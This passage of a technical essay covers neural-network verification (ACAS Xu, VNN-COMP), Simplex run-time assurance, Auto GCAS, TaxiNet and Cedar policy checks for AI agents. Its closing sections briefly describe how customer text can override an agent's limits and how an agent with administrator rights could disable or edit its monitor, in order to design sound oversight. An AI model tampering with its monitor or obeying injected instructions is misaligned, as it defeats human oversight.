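For example, Katz and colleagues look for an x between 0 and 1 that makes y at least 0.5. Every variable starts at zero. Reluplex raises y to 0.5, then raises the output of a to match, then the input of a, and then x. Finally, it sets the input of b to −0.5, which leaves the output of b at zero. All the constraints now hold, so Reluplex has found a solution, x = 0.5, without splitting into cases. On the ACAS Xu networks, it split on a ReLU only after repairing it five times. Once it had split on about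 10% of the ReLUs, the bounds it had derived often determined which case applied to each of the others.

No known method is fast on every network, because a ReLU network can encode a Boolean formula. If p, q and r are each 0 or 1, then 1 − max(0, 1 − p − q − r) is 1 when at least one of them is 1, and 0 otherwise, so a single ReLU can compute "p or q or r". A network can add up many such clauses, and checking whether the sum can reach the number of clauses is the same as checking whether all the clauses can be true at once. Katz and colleagues used this construction, with a few extra units to keep the inputs close to 0 or 1, to prove that verifying ReLU networks is NP-complete.

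They checked ten properties of the ACAS Xu prototype, including these:

| Property | Networks checked | Result | Computing time |
|---|---|---|---|
| If the other aircraft is far away and much slower, "clear of conflict" keeps a good score | 45 | Proved for 41, no answer for 4 | 4.6 days for the 41 |
| If it is straight ahead and approaching, the advisory is never "clear of conflict" | 42 | Proved for all | 7.8 hours |
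| If it is near and approaching from the left, the advisory is "strong right" | 1 | Proved | 5.4 hours |
| If vertical separation is large, the advisory is never a strong turn | 1 | No answer | |
| If vertical separation is large and the last advisory was "weak left", the next is the same or "clear of conflict" | 1 | Violated | 11.1 hours |

The violation was a real fault in which the network disagreed with the original table, and simulations had also revealed it. At least 35 networks violated another property, that "clear of conflict" never gets the worst score when the other aircraft is distant and slow. The researchers later decided that this behaviour was acceptable, so the specification was wrong in that case.

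### Safe advisories, unsafe flights

All these properties concern a single advisory, but an encounter can last minutes, and each turn changes the networks' next inputs. Bak and Tran (2022), in *Neural Network Compression of ACAS Xu Early Prototype is Unsafe*, checked whole encounters. They assumed perfect sensors, immediate turns and an intruder that flew straight at constant speed. They rounded positions, speeds and angles to a grid, started from every possible near-collision, and worked backwards second by second to see whether an ordinary encounter could lead there.

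Within about a minute they found encounters that did, and these also ended in near-collisions when replayed without rounding. In one, a slow drone was already moving out of the path of a faster aircraft behind it, and the networks turned it back into danger. Random testing is poor at finding such cases. In 1.5 million simulated encounters at constant altitude separation, it produced about 17 near-collisions, and their speeds varied less than those in the encounters the backward search found.

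Bak and Tran proved the rounded system safe when the drone flew at 1,000 to 1,200 feet per second, which is faster than most airliners. The networks were an early prototype, so their failures aren't evidence about any system in service. But the 2017 proofs, though correct within their scope, did not guarantee that a flight would be safe.

### From days to seconds

Verification has become much faster since Reluplex. Most leading tools now bound each unit's value above and below with linear functions of the network's inputs, which preserves relationships between units that plain intervals lose. They split the problem into cases only where the bounds are too loose, and they process many cases at once on GPUs.

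An annual competition tracks their progress. Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues (2025), in *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)*, report eight teams and 25 sets of problems. A year later there were 11 teams and 30 sets, according to Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*. Three tools now settle all 186 ACAS Xu queries, taking less than two minutes over each. These include the queries that defeated Reluplex. The overall winner, α,β-CROWN, did as follows on four of the sets:

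| Networks | Parameters in each | Queries | Settled |
|---|---|---|---|
| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | 186 | 186 |
| Small vision transformers | 68,000 to 76,000 | 200 | 123 |
| CIFAR-100 image classifiers | 2.5 to 3.8 million | 200 | 160 |
| VGG16 image classifier | 138 million | 18 | 18 |

Size is only one obstacle to verification. The VGG16 queries test whether small changes to an image can alter its label, and some involve changing only one pixel. Such a change probably leaves most units firmly on or off, so the verifier has few cases to check separately. Transformers, the type of network behind language models, are harder to verify because they multiply variables together and use functions more complicated than a ReLU. The entrants also propose the problems and vote on which ones count, so the results may overstate what the tools can do.

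The tools can be wrong. In the main part of the 2026 competition, eight of the 13 tools gave at least one answer that was incorrect or lacked a valid counterexample. The winner gave one such answer. The runner-up, Vibecheck, which its developers built over two months with the AI coding tool Claude Code, gave none. On the vision transformers, a tool called ACT reported proofs for all 200 queries. That may be a real advance, but the set's designers had removed nearly every query with a known counterexample, so a false proof would be hard to spot. The organisers hope eventually to require proofs that a separate program can check, which is also the idea behind Keel.

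### Real numbers and computer numbers

Most of these proofs treat weights and inputs as real numbers of unlimited precision, but computers round. Consider this unit:

```
y = max(0, (100000000 + x) - 100000000)
```

For real numbers, y equals x whenever x is positive. In 32-bit floating-point arithmetic, neighbouring numbers around 100 million are 8 apart. If x is 1, the first sum rounds back to 100 million and y is 0. Subtracting first would give the right answer, so the result depends on the order of operations, which can differ between chips or software libraries. Networks used in practice seldom contain such extreme numbers, but smaller errors of the same kind occur in nearly every layer.

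Kai Jia and Martin Rinard exploited this in *Exploiting Verified Neural Networks via Floating Point Numerical Error* (2021). They searched for images at the edge of what a verifier would certify, and found small changes that made the running network mislabel them even though the verifier had ruled out such errors.

The verifier can also make arithmetic errors. Katz and colleagues acknowledge that Reluplex used floating-point numbers for speed, and that their safeguards against rounding errors did not guarantee soundness. Rounding also complicated the competition's scoring. Earlier rules allowed counterexamples to miss the specification by a small margin, so two tools could be marked correct even if one proved a property and the other refuted it. Under the 2026 rules, a fixed version of one program checks each counterexample. Ladner and colleagues concede that this makes borderline verdicts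 reproducible but does not make them valid for every implementation.

An analyser can allow for rounding, as Astrée does for flight-control code. PyRAT, one of the three tools that settled every ACAS Xu query, also does this on ordinary processors, according to its developers. Bak and Tran's method avoids the problem by running the actual network on every point of the grid. This only works if the system also rounds its inputs to the grid in operation, and they point out that such a system behaves like a large lookup table.

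### No formula for a pedestrian

ACAS Xu is unusually easy to specify because its inputs are distances, angles and speeds, and engineers can describe a head-on approach in those terms. Some other aviation networks are similar. Collins Aerospace gave the competition networks that estimate how long an aircraft part will last. Their specifications include limits on the estimate for given ranges of sensor readings. Seven tools settled all 62 queries about these networks.

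A network that recognises pedestrians takes pixels as input. Nobody can write a formula over pixel values that is true exactly when an image shows a pedestrian, and such a formula would make the network unnecessary. Researchers usually prove robustness instead, which means that no sufficiently small change to a particular image alters its label. A wrong label can also be robust, and a network that always answers "no pedestrian" is robust on every image, so a proof of robustness does not show that the labels are correct.

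Even robustness is hard to achieve. One set of networks in the 2026 competition was trained with methods designed to make robustness easier to prove. One of these networks labelled 84% of test images correctly on CIFAR-10, a collection of small images in ten categories. Its developers could prove for only 66% of the images that the label was correct and would stay the same if each pixel's brightness changed by up to 2 levels out of 255. A network with the same design labelled 57% correctly and had proofs for 35% against changes of up to 8 levels.

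### Models that generate text step by step

A single pass through a language model is also a loop-free program. It produces a probability for each possible next token, which is a word or part of a word. William Merrill and Ashish Sabharwal proved in *The Parallelism Tradeoff* (2023) that one pass through a transformer can solve only problems that can be solved by circuits whose depth doesn't grow with the input, if the precision of the transformer's numbers grows only slowly with the input's length. Theorists widely believe that this rules out some simple-sounding tasks, such as telling whether there is a route from one point to another on an arbitrary map of one-way streets.

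To write text, however, software runs the model in a loop, adding each chosen token to the input until the model produces an end marker. In *The Expressive Power of Transformers with Chain of Thought* (2024), Merrill and Sabharwal proved that if the number of steps may grow polynomially with input length, transformers can solve exactly the problems that ordinary computers solve in polynomial time. Jorge Pérez, Javier Marinković and Pablo Barceló showed in 2019 that transformers are Turing-complete if both the number of steps and the precision are unlimited. Rice's theorem applies to such idealised models, so no algorithm can decide in general whether one will ever produce a forbidden sentence.

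These theorems show what some choice of weights could compute, not what trained models do reliably. Real models have limited precision, and operators cap the length of their output, so the questions are decidable in principle. As with any finite machine, this helps little in practice. An agent that can save notes to files and read them back is also not bound by the limit on how much text the model can take in at once. Dale Schuurmans showed in 2023 that a language model connected to an external memory can simulate a universal Turing machine.

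For language, researchers have so far mostly verified small networks used alongside a large model. One set of queries in the 2026 competition tests classifiers with a single layer of 128 ReLUs, which detect, for example, whether a user is asking if they are talking to a robot. A language model first converts each sentence into 30 numbers. Each query takes the smallest box that contains the numbers for a sentence and a set of its paraphrases, and checks whether the classifier labels every point in the box correctly. The best tools settled all 1,080 queries and found a mislabeled point in 662 of them. A successful proof does not cover paraphrases that fall outside the box, or the language model that produced the numbers.

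### What aviation authorities ask for

Aviation authorities are still writing their rules for machine learning. DO-178C assumes that engineers derive code from requirements, but *Finding Common Ground For Airborne Machine Learning Certification* (Bezzecchi, Fabre and Cofer, 2025) notes that machine learning infers functions from data.

EASA, the European aviation regulator, has proposed detailed specifications for trustworthy AI, partly in response to the EU's AI Act. According to Aviación al Día's *EASA publishes its first regulatory proposal on artificial intelligence in aviation* (2025), the specifications cover systems that assist people and systems that collaborate with them, and EASA planned a second proposal for 2026 to apply the framework to particular areas of aviation. The first proposal builds on EASA's 283-page *Guidance for Level 1 & 2 machine learning applications*.

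In a 2026 paper for Asia-Pacific aviation authorities, EASA summarises the evidence it wants. Developers must show that a system performs its intended function safely within a declared operational domain (the conditions it is designed for). They need requirements, verification, robustness tests and a link to the aircraft's safety assessment. They also have to control how they collect, select and label data, and show that the data are representative. Proofs like those for ACAS Xu could support part of this, particularly robustness, but they can't show that the training data were representative. EASA also expects performance monitoring, which matters because somebody has to notice when the aircraft leaves the declared domain.

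The industry's own standard is late. A joint committee of the standards bodies SAE International and EUROCAE has worked on machine learning since 2019. In August 2025, the two bodies aimed to publish their development guidelines, ED-324/ARP6983, in June 2026 (SAE International and EUROCAE, 2025). The committee's web page, EUROCAE's *WG-114*, still lists the document as a draft, with a target date of 31 December 2026.

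## Run-time assurance: a verified monitor around an unverified controller

Most neural networks are too large to verify as thoroughly as the ACAS Xu prototype, and for many of them nobody can write down what to prove. Engineers can leave such a network unverified and add a small, trusted program that takes over before the network does any damage. They call this run-time assurance. Its best-known form is the Simplex architecture, which *S3A* (2012) sums up as "using simplicity to control complexity". Early uses included pacemakers, avionics and a fleet of remote-controlled cars.

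A Simplex system has three parts. An advanced controller, which may be a learned model, normally runs the machine. A backup controller does the job less well but can keep the machine safe. A decision module chooses between them in every control cycle.

### Switching while the backup can still cope

A car doing 70 km/h one metre from a wall hasn't hit anything yet, but braking can't prevent the crash. The decision module therefore has to act well before anything goes wrong. *A Distributed Simplex Architecture for Multi-Agent Systems* (2020) makes this precise by defining two sets of states. The admissible states satisfy every safety constraint. The recoverable states are a smaller set, R, chosen so that if the system starts anywhere in R, the backup controller keeps it there. The car is in an admissible state but not a recoverable one.

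Let x be the current state and u the command that the advanced controller proposes. Next(x, u) is the set of all states the system might pass through before the next check, whatever the wind, load or friction within assumed limits. The switching rule is:

```
if Next(x, u) lies entirely within R:   carry out u
otherwise:                              hand over to the backup
```

The safety proof is an induction, like the one for the two railway routes. The system starts in R. At each step, the decision module either accepts u, having checked that u keeps the system in R, or hands control to the backup, which always keeps the system in R. The proof does not depend on how the advanced controller chose u.

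*The Black-Box Simplex Architecture for Runtime Assurance of Autonomous CPS* (2021) proves a theorem of this kind for a design in which the decision module checks whole sequences of commands. The system stays safe whatever the advanced controller outputs, provided that the module accepts a sequence only if it is permanently safe. A module that rejected every new sequence would also meet this condition. The paper's guarantee that a well-behaved controller stays in charge therefore also requires the module to accept every permanently safe sequence. In the terms used for analysers, the module must be sound to keep the system safe, and it must also be nearly complete to be useful.

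### A car that needs 44 metres

Suppose a learned model drives a car at 20 m/s (72 km/h), and the backup controller simply brakes. The brakes take 0.2 seconds to engage, during which the car covers 4 m at constant speed. They then slow it by 5 m/s every second, so it needs another 20² / (2 × 5) = 40 m to stop. At any speed v, the car is in a recoverable state if

```
gap >= 0.2 * v + v * v / 10
```

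At 20 m/s this comes to 44 m. But the decision module has to check where the car will be at the end of the cycle. If the module runs every tenth of a second and the model commands an acceleration of 3 m/s², the car will have covered about 2 m by the next check and will be doing 20.3 m/s, at which speed it needs 45.3 m to stop. The module should therefore accept the command only if the gap is now at least 47.3 m. A common shortcut is to skip the prediction and shrink R by a fixed margin, based on how fast the state can change and how long a cycle lasts.

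This check takes a few multiplications and a comparison, so engineers could prove it correct in almost any language. Squaring the speed causes no trouble in theory, because Alfred Tarski showed that arithmetic with addition and multiplication is decidable for real numbers, though it is undecidable for whole numbers.

The figure of 5 m/s² is harder to justify. On a wet road that allows only 4 m/s², the car needs 54 m. If the designers want to cover ice, at 1 m/s², the threshold rises to 204 m, and the car will brake for distant obstacles on dry roads too. *Context-dependent Runtime Construction of Safe Regions of Attraction from Design-Time Identification* (2026) makes the same point about Simplex in general, that its practical value depends on how conservative the safe region is. The paper's method constructs the region at run time to suit current conditions. Its experiments included a real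 platform controlled by a model trained to imitate demonstrations.

The decision module also needs an estimate of the gap. Suppose a neural network estimates it from a camera image and overestimates it by 10 m. When the true gap is 34 m, the decision module receives a value of 44 m and correctly hands over to the brakes. The car covers 4 m before they engage, which leaves 30 m. After 30 m of braking, its speed is the square root of 20² − 2 × 5 × 30, or 10 m/s, so it hits the obstacle at 36 km/h even though the switching code and every proof about it are correct.

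Engineers could raise the threshold to 54 m if they knew the error never exceeded 10 m, but no margin helps if the network doesn't detect the obstacle.

### Languages made for monitors

Researchers have designed restricted languages for writing monitors. NASA uses one called Copilot on experimental drones and rovers. *Trustworthy Runtime Verification via Bisimulation (Extended Experience Report)* (Scott, Perez and colleagues, 2026) illustrates it with a thermostat that turns the heating on when the average of the last five temperatures falls below 18°C, and off when it rises above 21°C. All five stored values start at 19.5°C, so a first reading of 38.2°C raises the average to 23.2°C and turns the heating off.

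Like Lustre, Copilot lets a program look back only a limited number of steps. The thermostat needs five readings, so the generated C program has an array of five numbers and overwrites the oldest at each step. The program contains no loops or recursion, so it can't hang.

Copilot is embedded in Haskell, a general-purpose language, so programmers can use all of Haskell to construct a monitor. Copilot then unfolds the result into a fixed list of equations, in which "the sum of the last five values" becomes four additions. A mistake in the Haskell code could hang the developer's computer but not the aircraft's.

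Scott and colleagues also built a tool that checks each generated C program against its Copilot source. It uses an SMT solver to prove that both start with the same values and that, if their values match before a step, they match after it and both trigger the same alarms. The thermostat requires 44 small proofs. While developing the tool, they found several bugs in Copilot's compiler, including one that made the C program give the sign of zero as 1 instead of 0. The project took just under a year, whereas proving an entire compiler correct has usually taken teams several years.

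A similar language, RTLola, has an analyser that calculates in advance how much memory and running time a monitor will need. *Monitoring Cyber-Physical Systems* (2020) explains that the analyser does this by drawing a graph of which values depend on which. For example, if a rule compares a drone's altitude with its altitude three readings ago, the monitor must keep three past readings. *Two Ways to See the Future* (2026) proves that the calculated memory is enough even when rules refer to later readings, which the monitor has to wait for.

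*RTLola Cleared for Take-Off* (Baumeister, Finkbeiner and colleagues, 2020) describes monitors for unmanned aircraft at DLR, the German Aerospace Center. The researchers translated the monitors' rules into a circuit on a programmable chip. As *Restart-Based Fault-Tolerance* (2017) points out, Simplex's guarantee fails if an operating-system fault crashes the decision module or the backup. Putting the monitor on a separate chip helps with this weakness. Researchers have also applied RTLola to an electric aircraft made by Volocopter, according to *A Tutorial on Stream-based Monitoring* (2025).

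RTLola has grown more expressive, as eBPF did. A newer version lets a monitor create any number of copies of a rule while running, for instance one for each aircraft nearby. *Type-safe Monitoring of Parameterized Streams* (Baumeister, Finkbeiner and Kohn, 2026) shows that no algorithm can determine in general whether a monitor in this version is free of run-time errors, such as reading from a copy that doesn't exist. The paper restores the guarantee with a type system that requires every such read either to provably succeed or to have a default value. Some harmless monitors will inevitably fail this test, but adding a default usually fixes them. Somebody then has to consider what the default means, because a monitor that uses a default distance of 10 km for a missing aircraft will ignore that aircraft.

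### Auto GCAS and the unverified pilot

In the run-time assurance system with the best record, the untrusted controller is a human pilot. Since late 2014, US Air Force F-16s have carried the Automatic Ground Collision Avoidance System (Auto GCAS), which Lockheed Martin developed with NASA and the Air Force Research Laboratory (AFRL). According to Lockheed Martin's *Auto GCAS*, the system uses precise navigation, aircraft performance data and a digital terrain map to predict whether the jet is about to hit the ground. If so, it rolls the wings level and pulls up at 5 g. It acts at the last moment, so pilots can still fly low on purpose, and they can override it.

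In one case, a student pilot lost consciousness during a high-speed manoeuvre and the jet headed for the ground. Auto GCAS had begun to level it by the time the pilot came round. Lockheed Martin's page from around 2019 credits the system with saving 13 pilots and 12 aircraft, while AFRL's *Automatic Ground Collision Avoidance* counts 12 pilots and 11 aircraft. Both organisations have an interest in a high count, but a diving jet with an unconscious pilot would almost certainly crash. AFRL also estimates that Auto GCAS can prevent 98% of crashes in which a pilot flies a working F-16 into the ground. These crashes account for three quarters of F-16 pilot deaths.

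The US Navy's Super Hornets and Growlers have had a system that only warns the pilot, according to The Aviationist's *U.S. Navy Looking to Add AGCAS to Super Hornets and Growlers* (2025), and a warning can't help an unconscious pilot. AIAA's *Navy and Marines Corps Set to Install Automatic Ground Collision Avoidance Systems* (2025) relays a report that the Navy and Marine Corps will install the automatic version and that they admit it could have prevented several fatal crashes.

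This record supports the architecture but provides little evidence about programming languages. The most important factor is probably how well defined the problem is. The ground doesn't move, one manoeuvre nearly always avoids it, and the system relies on GPS and a terrain database, as AFRL notes, rather than on a learned model. Even this data is incomplete, since the database won't include a crane put up last week.

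### AI pilots on the X-62A

The X-62A is a modified F-16 that the US Air Force Test Pilot School uses to test experimental flight controls. Learned models began flying it in late 2022, and one flew a mock dogfight against a human pilot in September 2023. The system that protects the aircraft from their errors dates from the 1990s. The Air Current reports that this system of "safety trips" monitors more than 200 limits. When the aircraft approaches one, the system disengages the experimental controller, stabilises the aircraft and hands control to a safety pilot.

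The school left the safety trips unchanged for the AI tests, which let the team change almost everything else quickly. According to Edwards Air Force Base, where the school is based, the team changed over 100,000 lines of flight-critical software across 21 test flights, in which the jets came within 2,000 feet of each other. DVIDS, the US military's media service, reports that the safety pilots never had to switch off the AI during the dogfights. This refers to the pilots' own switch, so we can't infer from it how often the automatic trips fired.

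In April 2026, AI agents on the X-62A intercepted airborne targets 27 times in eight flights, using live data from an infrared sensor (D'Urso, *X-62 VISTA Conducts AI-Controlled Intercepts with IRST Pod*, 2026). A parallel programme tested new rules to keep autonomous aircraft within limits set by their operators (Kohler, *X-62 VISTA sets precedents with Mission Systems Upgrades*). By July, an AI agent was also flying an ordinary F-16 fitted with a control kit, according to DARPA, the Pentagon's research agency (2026). A pilot on board can take back control with a switch.

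A barrier function allows a gentler intervention than an abrupt handover. It is a quantity h that is positive while the vehicle is safe and zero at the limit. In the simplest version, a filter limits how fast h can fall, in proportion to h. For the car, h could be the gap minus the stopping distance. If the filter lets h shrink by at most half its value per second, h can fall at 5 m/s when it is 10 m but only at 1 m/s when it is 2 m. *Safety Guardrails in the Sky* (2026) describes a week of flights on the X-62A with a filter based on this idea. The filter smoothly blends the pilot's commands with those of a backup controller. It completed all 14 test points, including some in which the pilot deliberately tried to break the limits. A human flew the aircraft in these tests, and a week is only long enough to try a few ways of breaking a limit.

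### What ASTM F3269 requires

ASTM's *Standard Practice for Methods to Safely Bound Behavior of Aircraft Systems* (2021), known as F3269, standardizes this architecture, mainly for drones. Its "complex function" can be anything that hasn't gone through normal aviation development, including a machine-learning model or, as in its Auto GCAS example, a human pilot. The parts around it must meet whatever level of assurance a safety assessment requires. The standard doesn't prescribe a programming language.

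ASTM requires designers to work out where the protection applies. For each recovery function, they determine the conditions in which it can keep the aircraft safe, and for each monitor, the conditions in which it can detect trouble. The coverage is then

```
(RF1 ∪ RF2 ∪ ...) ∩ (M1 ∪ M2 ∪ ...)
```

where RF1 is the set of conditions that the first recovery function can handle, M1 the set for the first monitor, and so on. On a dry road in fog, the car's brakes work but its monitor may be blind. On ice in clear weather, the monitor can see but the brakes are too weak. Only dry roads in clear weather are covered, and designers must ensure that nobody relies on the system anywhere else. They also have to account for every delay between the sensor reading and the completed recovery.

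Under the standard, the monitor and the recovery function may use only "assured" data. An input manager checks everything else, for example by rejecting compass headings outside 0 to 360 degrees and comparing successive values with a model of how they should change. These checks would catch many faults but not the 10 m error in the braking example, because the estimated gap stays in range and shrinks at the same rate as the true gap. As the true gap falls from 34 m to 32 m and then 30 m, the estimate falls from 44 m to 42 m and then 40 m. A radar that measured the gap independently would expose the error.

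Collins Aerospace's slide deck *Run Time Assurance Architecture for Learning Enabled Systems* (2020) claims that a learned component may still behave unexpectedly but that the architecture keeps this from affecting safety. This is true only when the learned component is the controller, because a learned sensor can give wrong data to the monitor as well.

### TaxiNet: when the sensor is a neural network

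TaxiNet is the neural network in an experimental Boeing system that keeps an aircraft on the centreline of a taxiway. It uses images from a camera on the right wing to estimate the aircraft's distance from the line and its angle to it, and a controller steers based on those estimates. Boeing's main requirement, according to *Formal Analysis and Redesign of a Neural Network-Based Aircraft Taxiing System* (2020), was that the aircraft should always stay within 1.5 m of the line.

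A monitor could check this with a single comparison if it had the true distance. But if TaxiNet estimates 0.5 m when the true distance is 2 m, a monitor that relies on TaxiNet will not intervene. A precise satellite positioning system could supply an independent measurement, but an aircraft with such a trusted source would have less need for TaxiNet.

Researchers have looked for ways to do without one. The 2020 study searched for failures in a flight simulator, varying conditions such as the aircraft's starting position and the time of day. *Closed-loop Analysis of Vision-based Autonomous Systems* (2023) treats perception errors as random and models the aircraft, controller and network together as a Markov chain, in which the current state determines the probability of each possible next state. The model gives the probability that the aircraft leaves the centreline, but this estimate is only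 as accurate as the measured error rates.

*Assumption Generation for the Verification of Learning-Enabled Autonomous Systems* (2023) starts by assuming that the network's estimates could be arbitrarily wrong, then works out what conditions they must meet for the aircraft to stay safe. This is useful because it turns a requirement on the aircraft into one on the network, but someone still has to show that the network meets it.

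The most promising approach accounts for the network's uncertainty. *Conformal Safety Shielding for Imperfect-Perception Agents* (2025) divides the aircraft's possible positions and angles into 15 states. For each picture, the software produces a set of candidate states instead of one answer, and it allows an action only if it is safe for every state in the set. If the set includes both "left of the line" and "on the line", for example, the aircraft may not steer further left. The paper uses pictures with known positions to make the sets large enough to contain the true state at a chosen rate.

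If each set has a 99% chance of containing the true state and errors are independent, the chance that all the sets for 100 pictures in a row contain it is 0.99^100, or about 37%. One miss might not take the aircraft off the taxiway, but this guarantee is much weaker than the Simplex theorem. The 99% rate also holds only while new pictures resemble the ones used for calibration.

### An AI agent at a computer

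Auto GCAS works because a few numbers describe the danger, trusted instruments measure them, and a known manoeuvre avoids the danger. These conditions hold for only some of the tasks an AI agent does on a computer.

The shop could describe part of its risk with two numbers, today's total refunds and the amount of the next refund, and refuse any that would take the total over a daily limit. An agent with command-line access is much harder to contain, because the state of the system includes every file, account and program the agent can reach. The agent can also write new programs, and no monitor can always predict what they will do.

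Physics also limits how fast a car can get into danger. At 20 m/s it moves only 2 m in a tenth of a second, so a decision module can leave a margin for whatever happens before the next check. On a computer, one command can delete years of work, but designers can impose their own rate limits. If the payment system releases at most 500 euros an hour, and somebody who can halt it reviews the refunds every four hours, the agent can lose at most 2,000 euros between reviews.

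Some of the agent's inputs are more reliable than any camera image. The amount in a refund request and the price in the shop's database are exact numbers. But the claim that the kettle arrived broken comes from a customer's message, and a language model that judges such claims is in the same position as TaxiNet. It is worse off in one respect, because a dishonest customer can keep rewording the message until the model accepts it. A second language model that checks the first could also accept the false claim, perhaps because of the same message.

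The agent often has a better fallback than a jet, which can't stop in mid-air, because the monitor can refuse a request and leave it for staff. But stopping isn't always safe. An agent that stops halfway through moving a database may leave it unusable, and stopping can't undo an email that has already been sent. Actions like these can take the system out of its recoverable states in a single step, so the monitor has to check them before they happen. Designers can also make more states recoverable. If the shop holds all refunds until the evening, staff have the rest of the day to cancel a bad one.

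Simplex also assumes that the advanced controller can't tamper with the decision module. An agent with administrator rights on the monitor's computer could stop the monitor or edit its limits, so the monitor should run on a separate machine and hold the payment password itself. The theorem says that the system is safe whatever the controller outputs, so it would then cover even an agent trying to do harm, if the agent could act only through those outputs and the designers' model included everything those outputs could do.

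## Cedar: analysable rules for single actions by AI agents

Amazon Web Services (AWS) offers a service called Bedrock AgentCore for running AI agents. Its gateway passes an agent's requests on to tools, such as a shop's refund system, and can first check each request against a set of rules. These checks have been generally available since March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). Customers can write the rules in Cedar, a restricted language that AWS designed for deciding who may do what.

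To issue a refund, the language model outputs a call to the refund tool with an order number, an amount and a reason. The software around the model sends this call to the gateway, along with a signed token that identifies the user. The gateway turns both into a Cedar request with four parts: the principal (the user), the action (the tool), the resource (here the gateway) and the context (the arguments of the call). The gateway forwards the call to the refund tool only if the rules allow the request.

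AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* explains that the check sits outside the model because the model can't be trusted. A customer's message may contain text that the model mistakes for instructions, and these can override any limits the shop wrote into the model's prompt. Checks inside each tool's code are more robust, but they are hard to audit when scattered across many tools. Amazon is selling the external check, but its reasoning holds up. Much the same reasoning applied to the Simplex architecture, where the safety proof didn't depend on how the untrusted controller chose its commands.

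The gateway also hides any tool that the rules would always refuse. AWS claims this removes a whole class of risk, because an agent can't try to call a tool it doesn't know exists. But an agent could guess the tool's name or read it in a document, so the protection still depends on the gateway refusing the call.

### Permit and forbid

With some long names shortened, a refund rule might look like this:

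```
permit (principal, action == Action::"refund", resource)
when   { context.input.amount <= 100 }
unless { context.input.reason == "changed mind" };
```

It allows refunds of up to 100 euros, except when the customer has simply changed their mind. Cedar also has `forbid` rules, which take the same form. A request succeeds only if at least one `permit` rule matches it and no `forbid` rule does. The order of the rules makes no difference.

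According to *Cedar* (Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues, 2024), a rule can compare values, combine conditions with "and", "or" and "not", test whether a user belongs to a group, and match text against simple patterns. It can also add and subtract whole numbers and multiply them by constants. A rule can't use general loops, store or change anything, or contact another system. Checking a request therefore always finishes, usually in time proportional to the size of the rules and at worst in quadratic time.

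Cedar ignores any rule that fails with an error, as Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues explain in *How We Built Cedar* (2024). This is harmless for a `permit` rule, because Cedar denies the request if nothing else permits it, but ignoring a `forbid` rule can let through a request the rule was meant to block. Suppose the shop permits all refunds, then forbids those over 500 euros with a rule that converts the amount to cents, `amount * 100 > 50000`. For a refund of 100 quadrillion euros, the multiplication overflows Cedar's 64-bit integers, so the `forbid` rule fails and Cedar allows the refund.

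Cedar's validator checks rules against a schema, which describes what requests can contain. It would reject a rule that reads an optional argument without first checking that the argument is present, but it doesn't rule out overflow. The shop could avoid the problem by putting the limit in the `permit` rule, where an error leads to a refusal.

### From rules to formulas

Cedar's main attraction for a control layer is that a computer can answer questions about the rules for every possible request. A program called a symbolic compiler translates the rules into formulas for an SMT solver. In the refund rule, the amount becomes an unknown 64-bit number a, and the reason becomes an unknown string r:

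```
old(a, r):   a <= 100  and  not (r = "changed mind")
```

Groups are harder to translate. In Cedar, one group can belong to another, but no group can contain itself, directly or through other groups. If the formulas left this out, the solver could report a problem that arises only in an impossible case, such as when the night shift belongs to the support team and the support team belongs to the night shift. Cedar's compiler states the condition separately for each user or group that the rules can refer to, because a single condition about "every group" would make the formulas undecidable, and the solver may then time out. The rules have no general loops, so the list of these users and groups is finite and the compiler can work it out from the rules' text.

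Cutler and colleagues describe the resulting translation as decidable, sound and complete. An algorithm can settle every formula the translation produces, and the analysis misses no violations among requests that fit the schema and raises no false alarms. Astrée and the eBPF verifier can raise false alarms, but Cedar's designers avoided them by keeping the language small.

The formulas also use the same 64-bit arithmetic as the rules, whereas most of the proofs about ACAS Xu treated computer numbers as if they had unlimited precision. If the shop checked whether its `forbid` rule blocks every refund above 500 euros, the analysis would find the overflow.

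Decidability doesn't guarantee speed, because the formulas include ordinary Boolean logic. A sufficiently awkward set of rules could still defeat the solver in practice.

### An edit that looks stricter

Suppose somebody at the shop changes the last line of the refund rule to

```
unless { context.input.reason == "changed mind" && context.input.amount > 50 };
```

The new line has an extra condition, so it may look stricter. In fact it is looser, because the exception now applies to fewer requests. The new formula is

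```
new(a, r):   a <= 100  and  not (r = "changed mind" and a > 50)
```

To find out what the edit newly allows, the analyser uses the solver to find values that make `new` true and `old` false. For `new` to be true, a must be at most 100. For those amounts, `old` is false only if r is "changed mind". When r is "changed mind", `new` is true only if a is at most 50. The edit therefore newly allows exactly the requests where the customer changed their mind and the amount is 50 euros or less. The solver returns one of them, such as a refund of 30 euros.

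The analyser then checks whether any request satisfies `old` but not `new`. None does, so the edited rule is strictly more permissive. AWS's *Introducing Cedar Analysis* describes a free tool that makes this comparison and reports one of four results: equivalent, more permissive, less permissive or incomparable.

Tests could easily miss the change. If the shop tested a 60-euro refund for a broken kettle and an 80-euro refund for a customer who changed their mind, both versions would allow the first and refuse the second. *AutoCedar* (2026) points out that testing compares policies only on a finite set of requests.

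The solver might also return a refund of −40 euros, because neither version requires the amount to be positive. Depending on how the payment system handles negative numbers, this could charge the customer. The shop would learn of this possibility from the example, even though nobody had asked about negative refunds.

The analyser can't determine whether the shop wanted to allow small refunds to people who change their minds. It compares one formal statement with another, and somebody has to supply both. In AWS's own documentation, *Understanding Cedar policies*, for example, the English requirement is a limit of "$500 or less", but the rule is `amount < 500`, which refuses a refund of exactly $500. A search for rules that are contradictory or allow everything would not flag this one. If somebody also wrote the requirement as a Cedar rule, with `<= 500`, a comparison would find the difference.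 *AutoCedar* relies on the fact that many requirements can be written this way. But the second rule can be wrong too, particularly if the same person writes both.

### Speed

Cutler and colleagues compared Cedar with two other open-source languages, Rego and OpenFGA. Rego is the language of Open Policy Agent, a general-purpose system for checking rules. OpenFGA is designed for permissions that depend on relationships, such as letting the owner of a folder edit every document in it. Cedar was 28.7 to 35.2 times as fast as OpenFGA and 42.8 to 80.8 times as fast as Rego on three example applications, for sharing files, hosting code and managing to-do lists.

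Most of the researchers worked at Amazon, and the three examples suited Cedar because they depend on chains of membership, for which Cedar has a built-in operator and Rego doesn't. The researchers acknowledge that Rego scales much better if the application works out the chains in advance. They also note that OpenFGA's developers had not optimised the in-memory storage used in the test.

In the largest file-sharing test, Rego's median decision took 676 microseconds and Cedar's took 5. Both times are negligible for an AI agent if its language model needs a second or more to produce the request.

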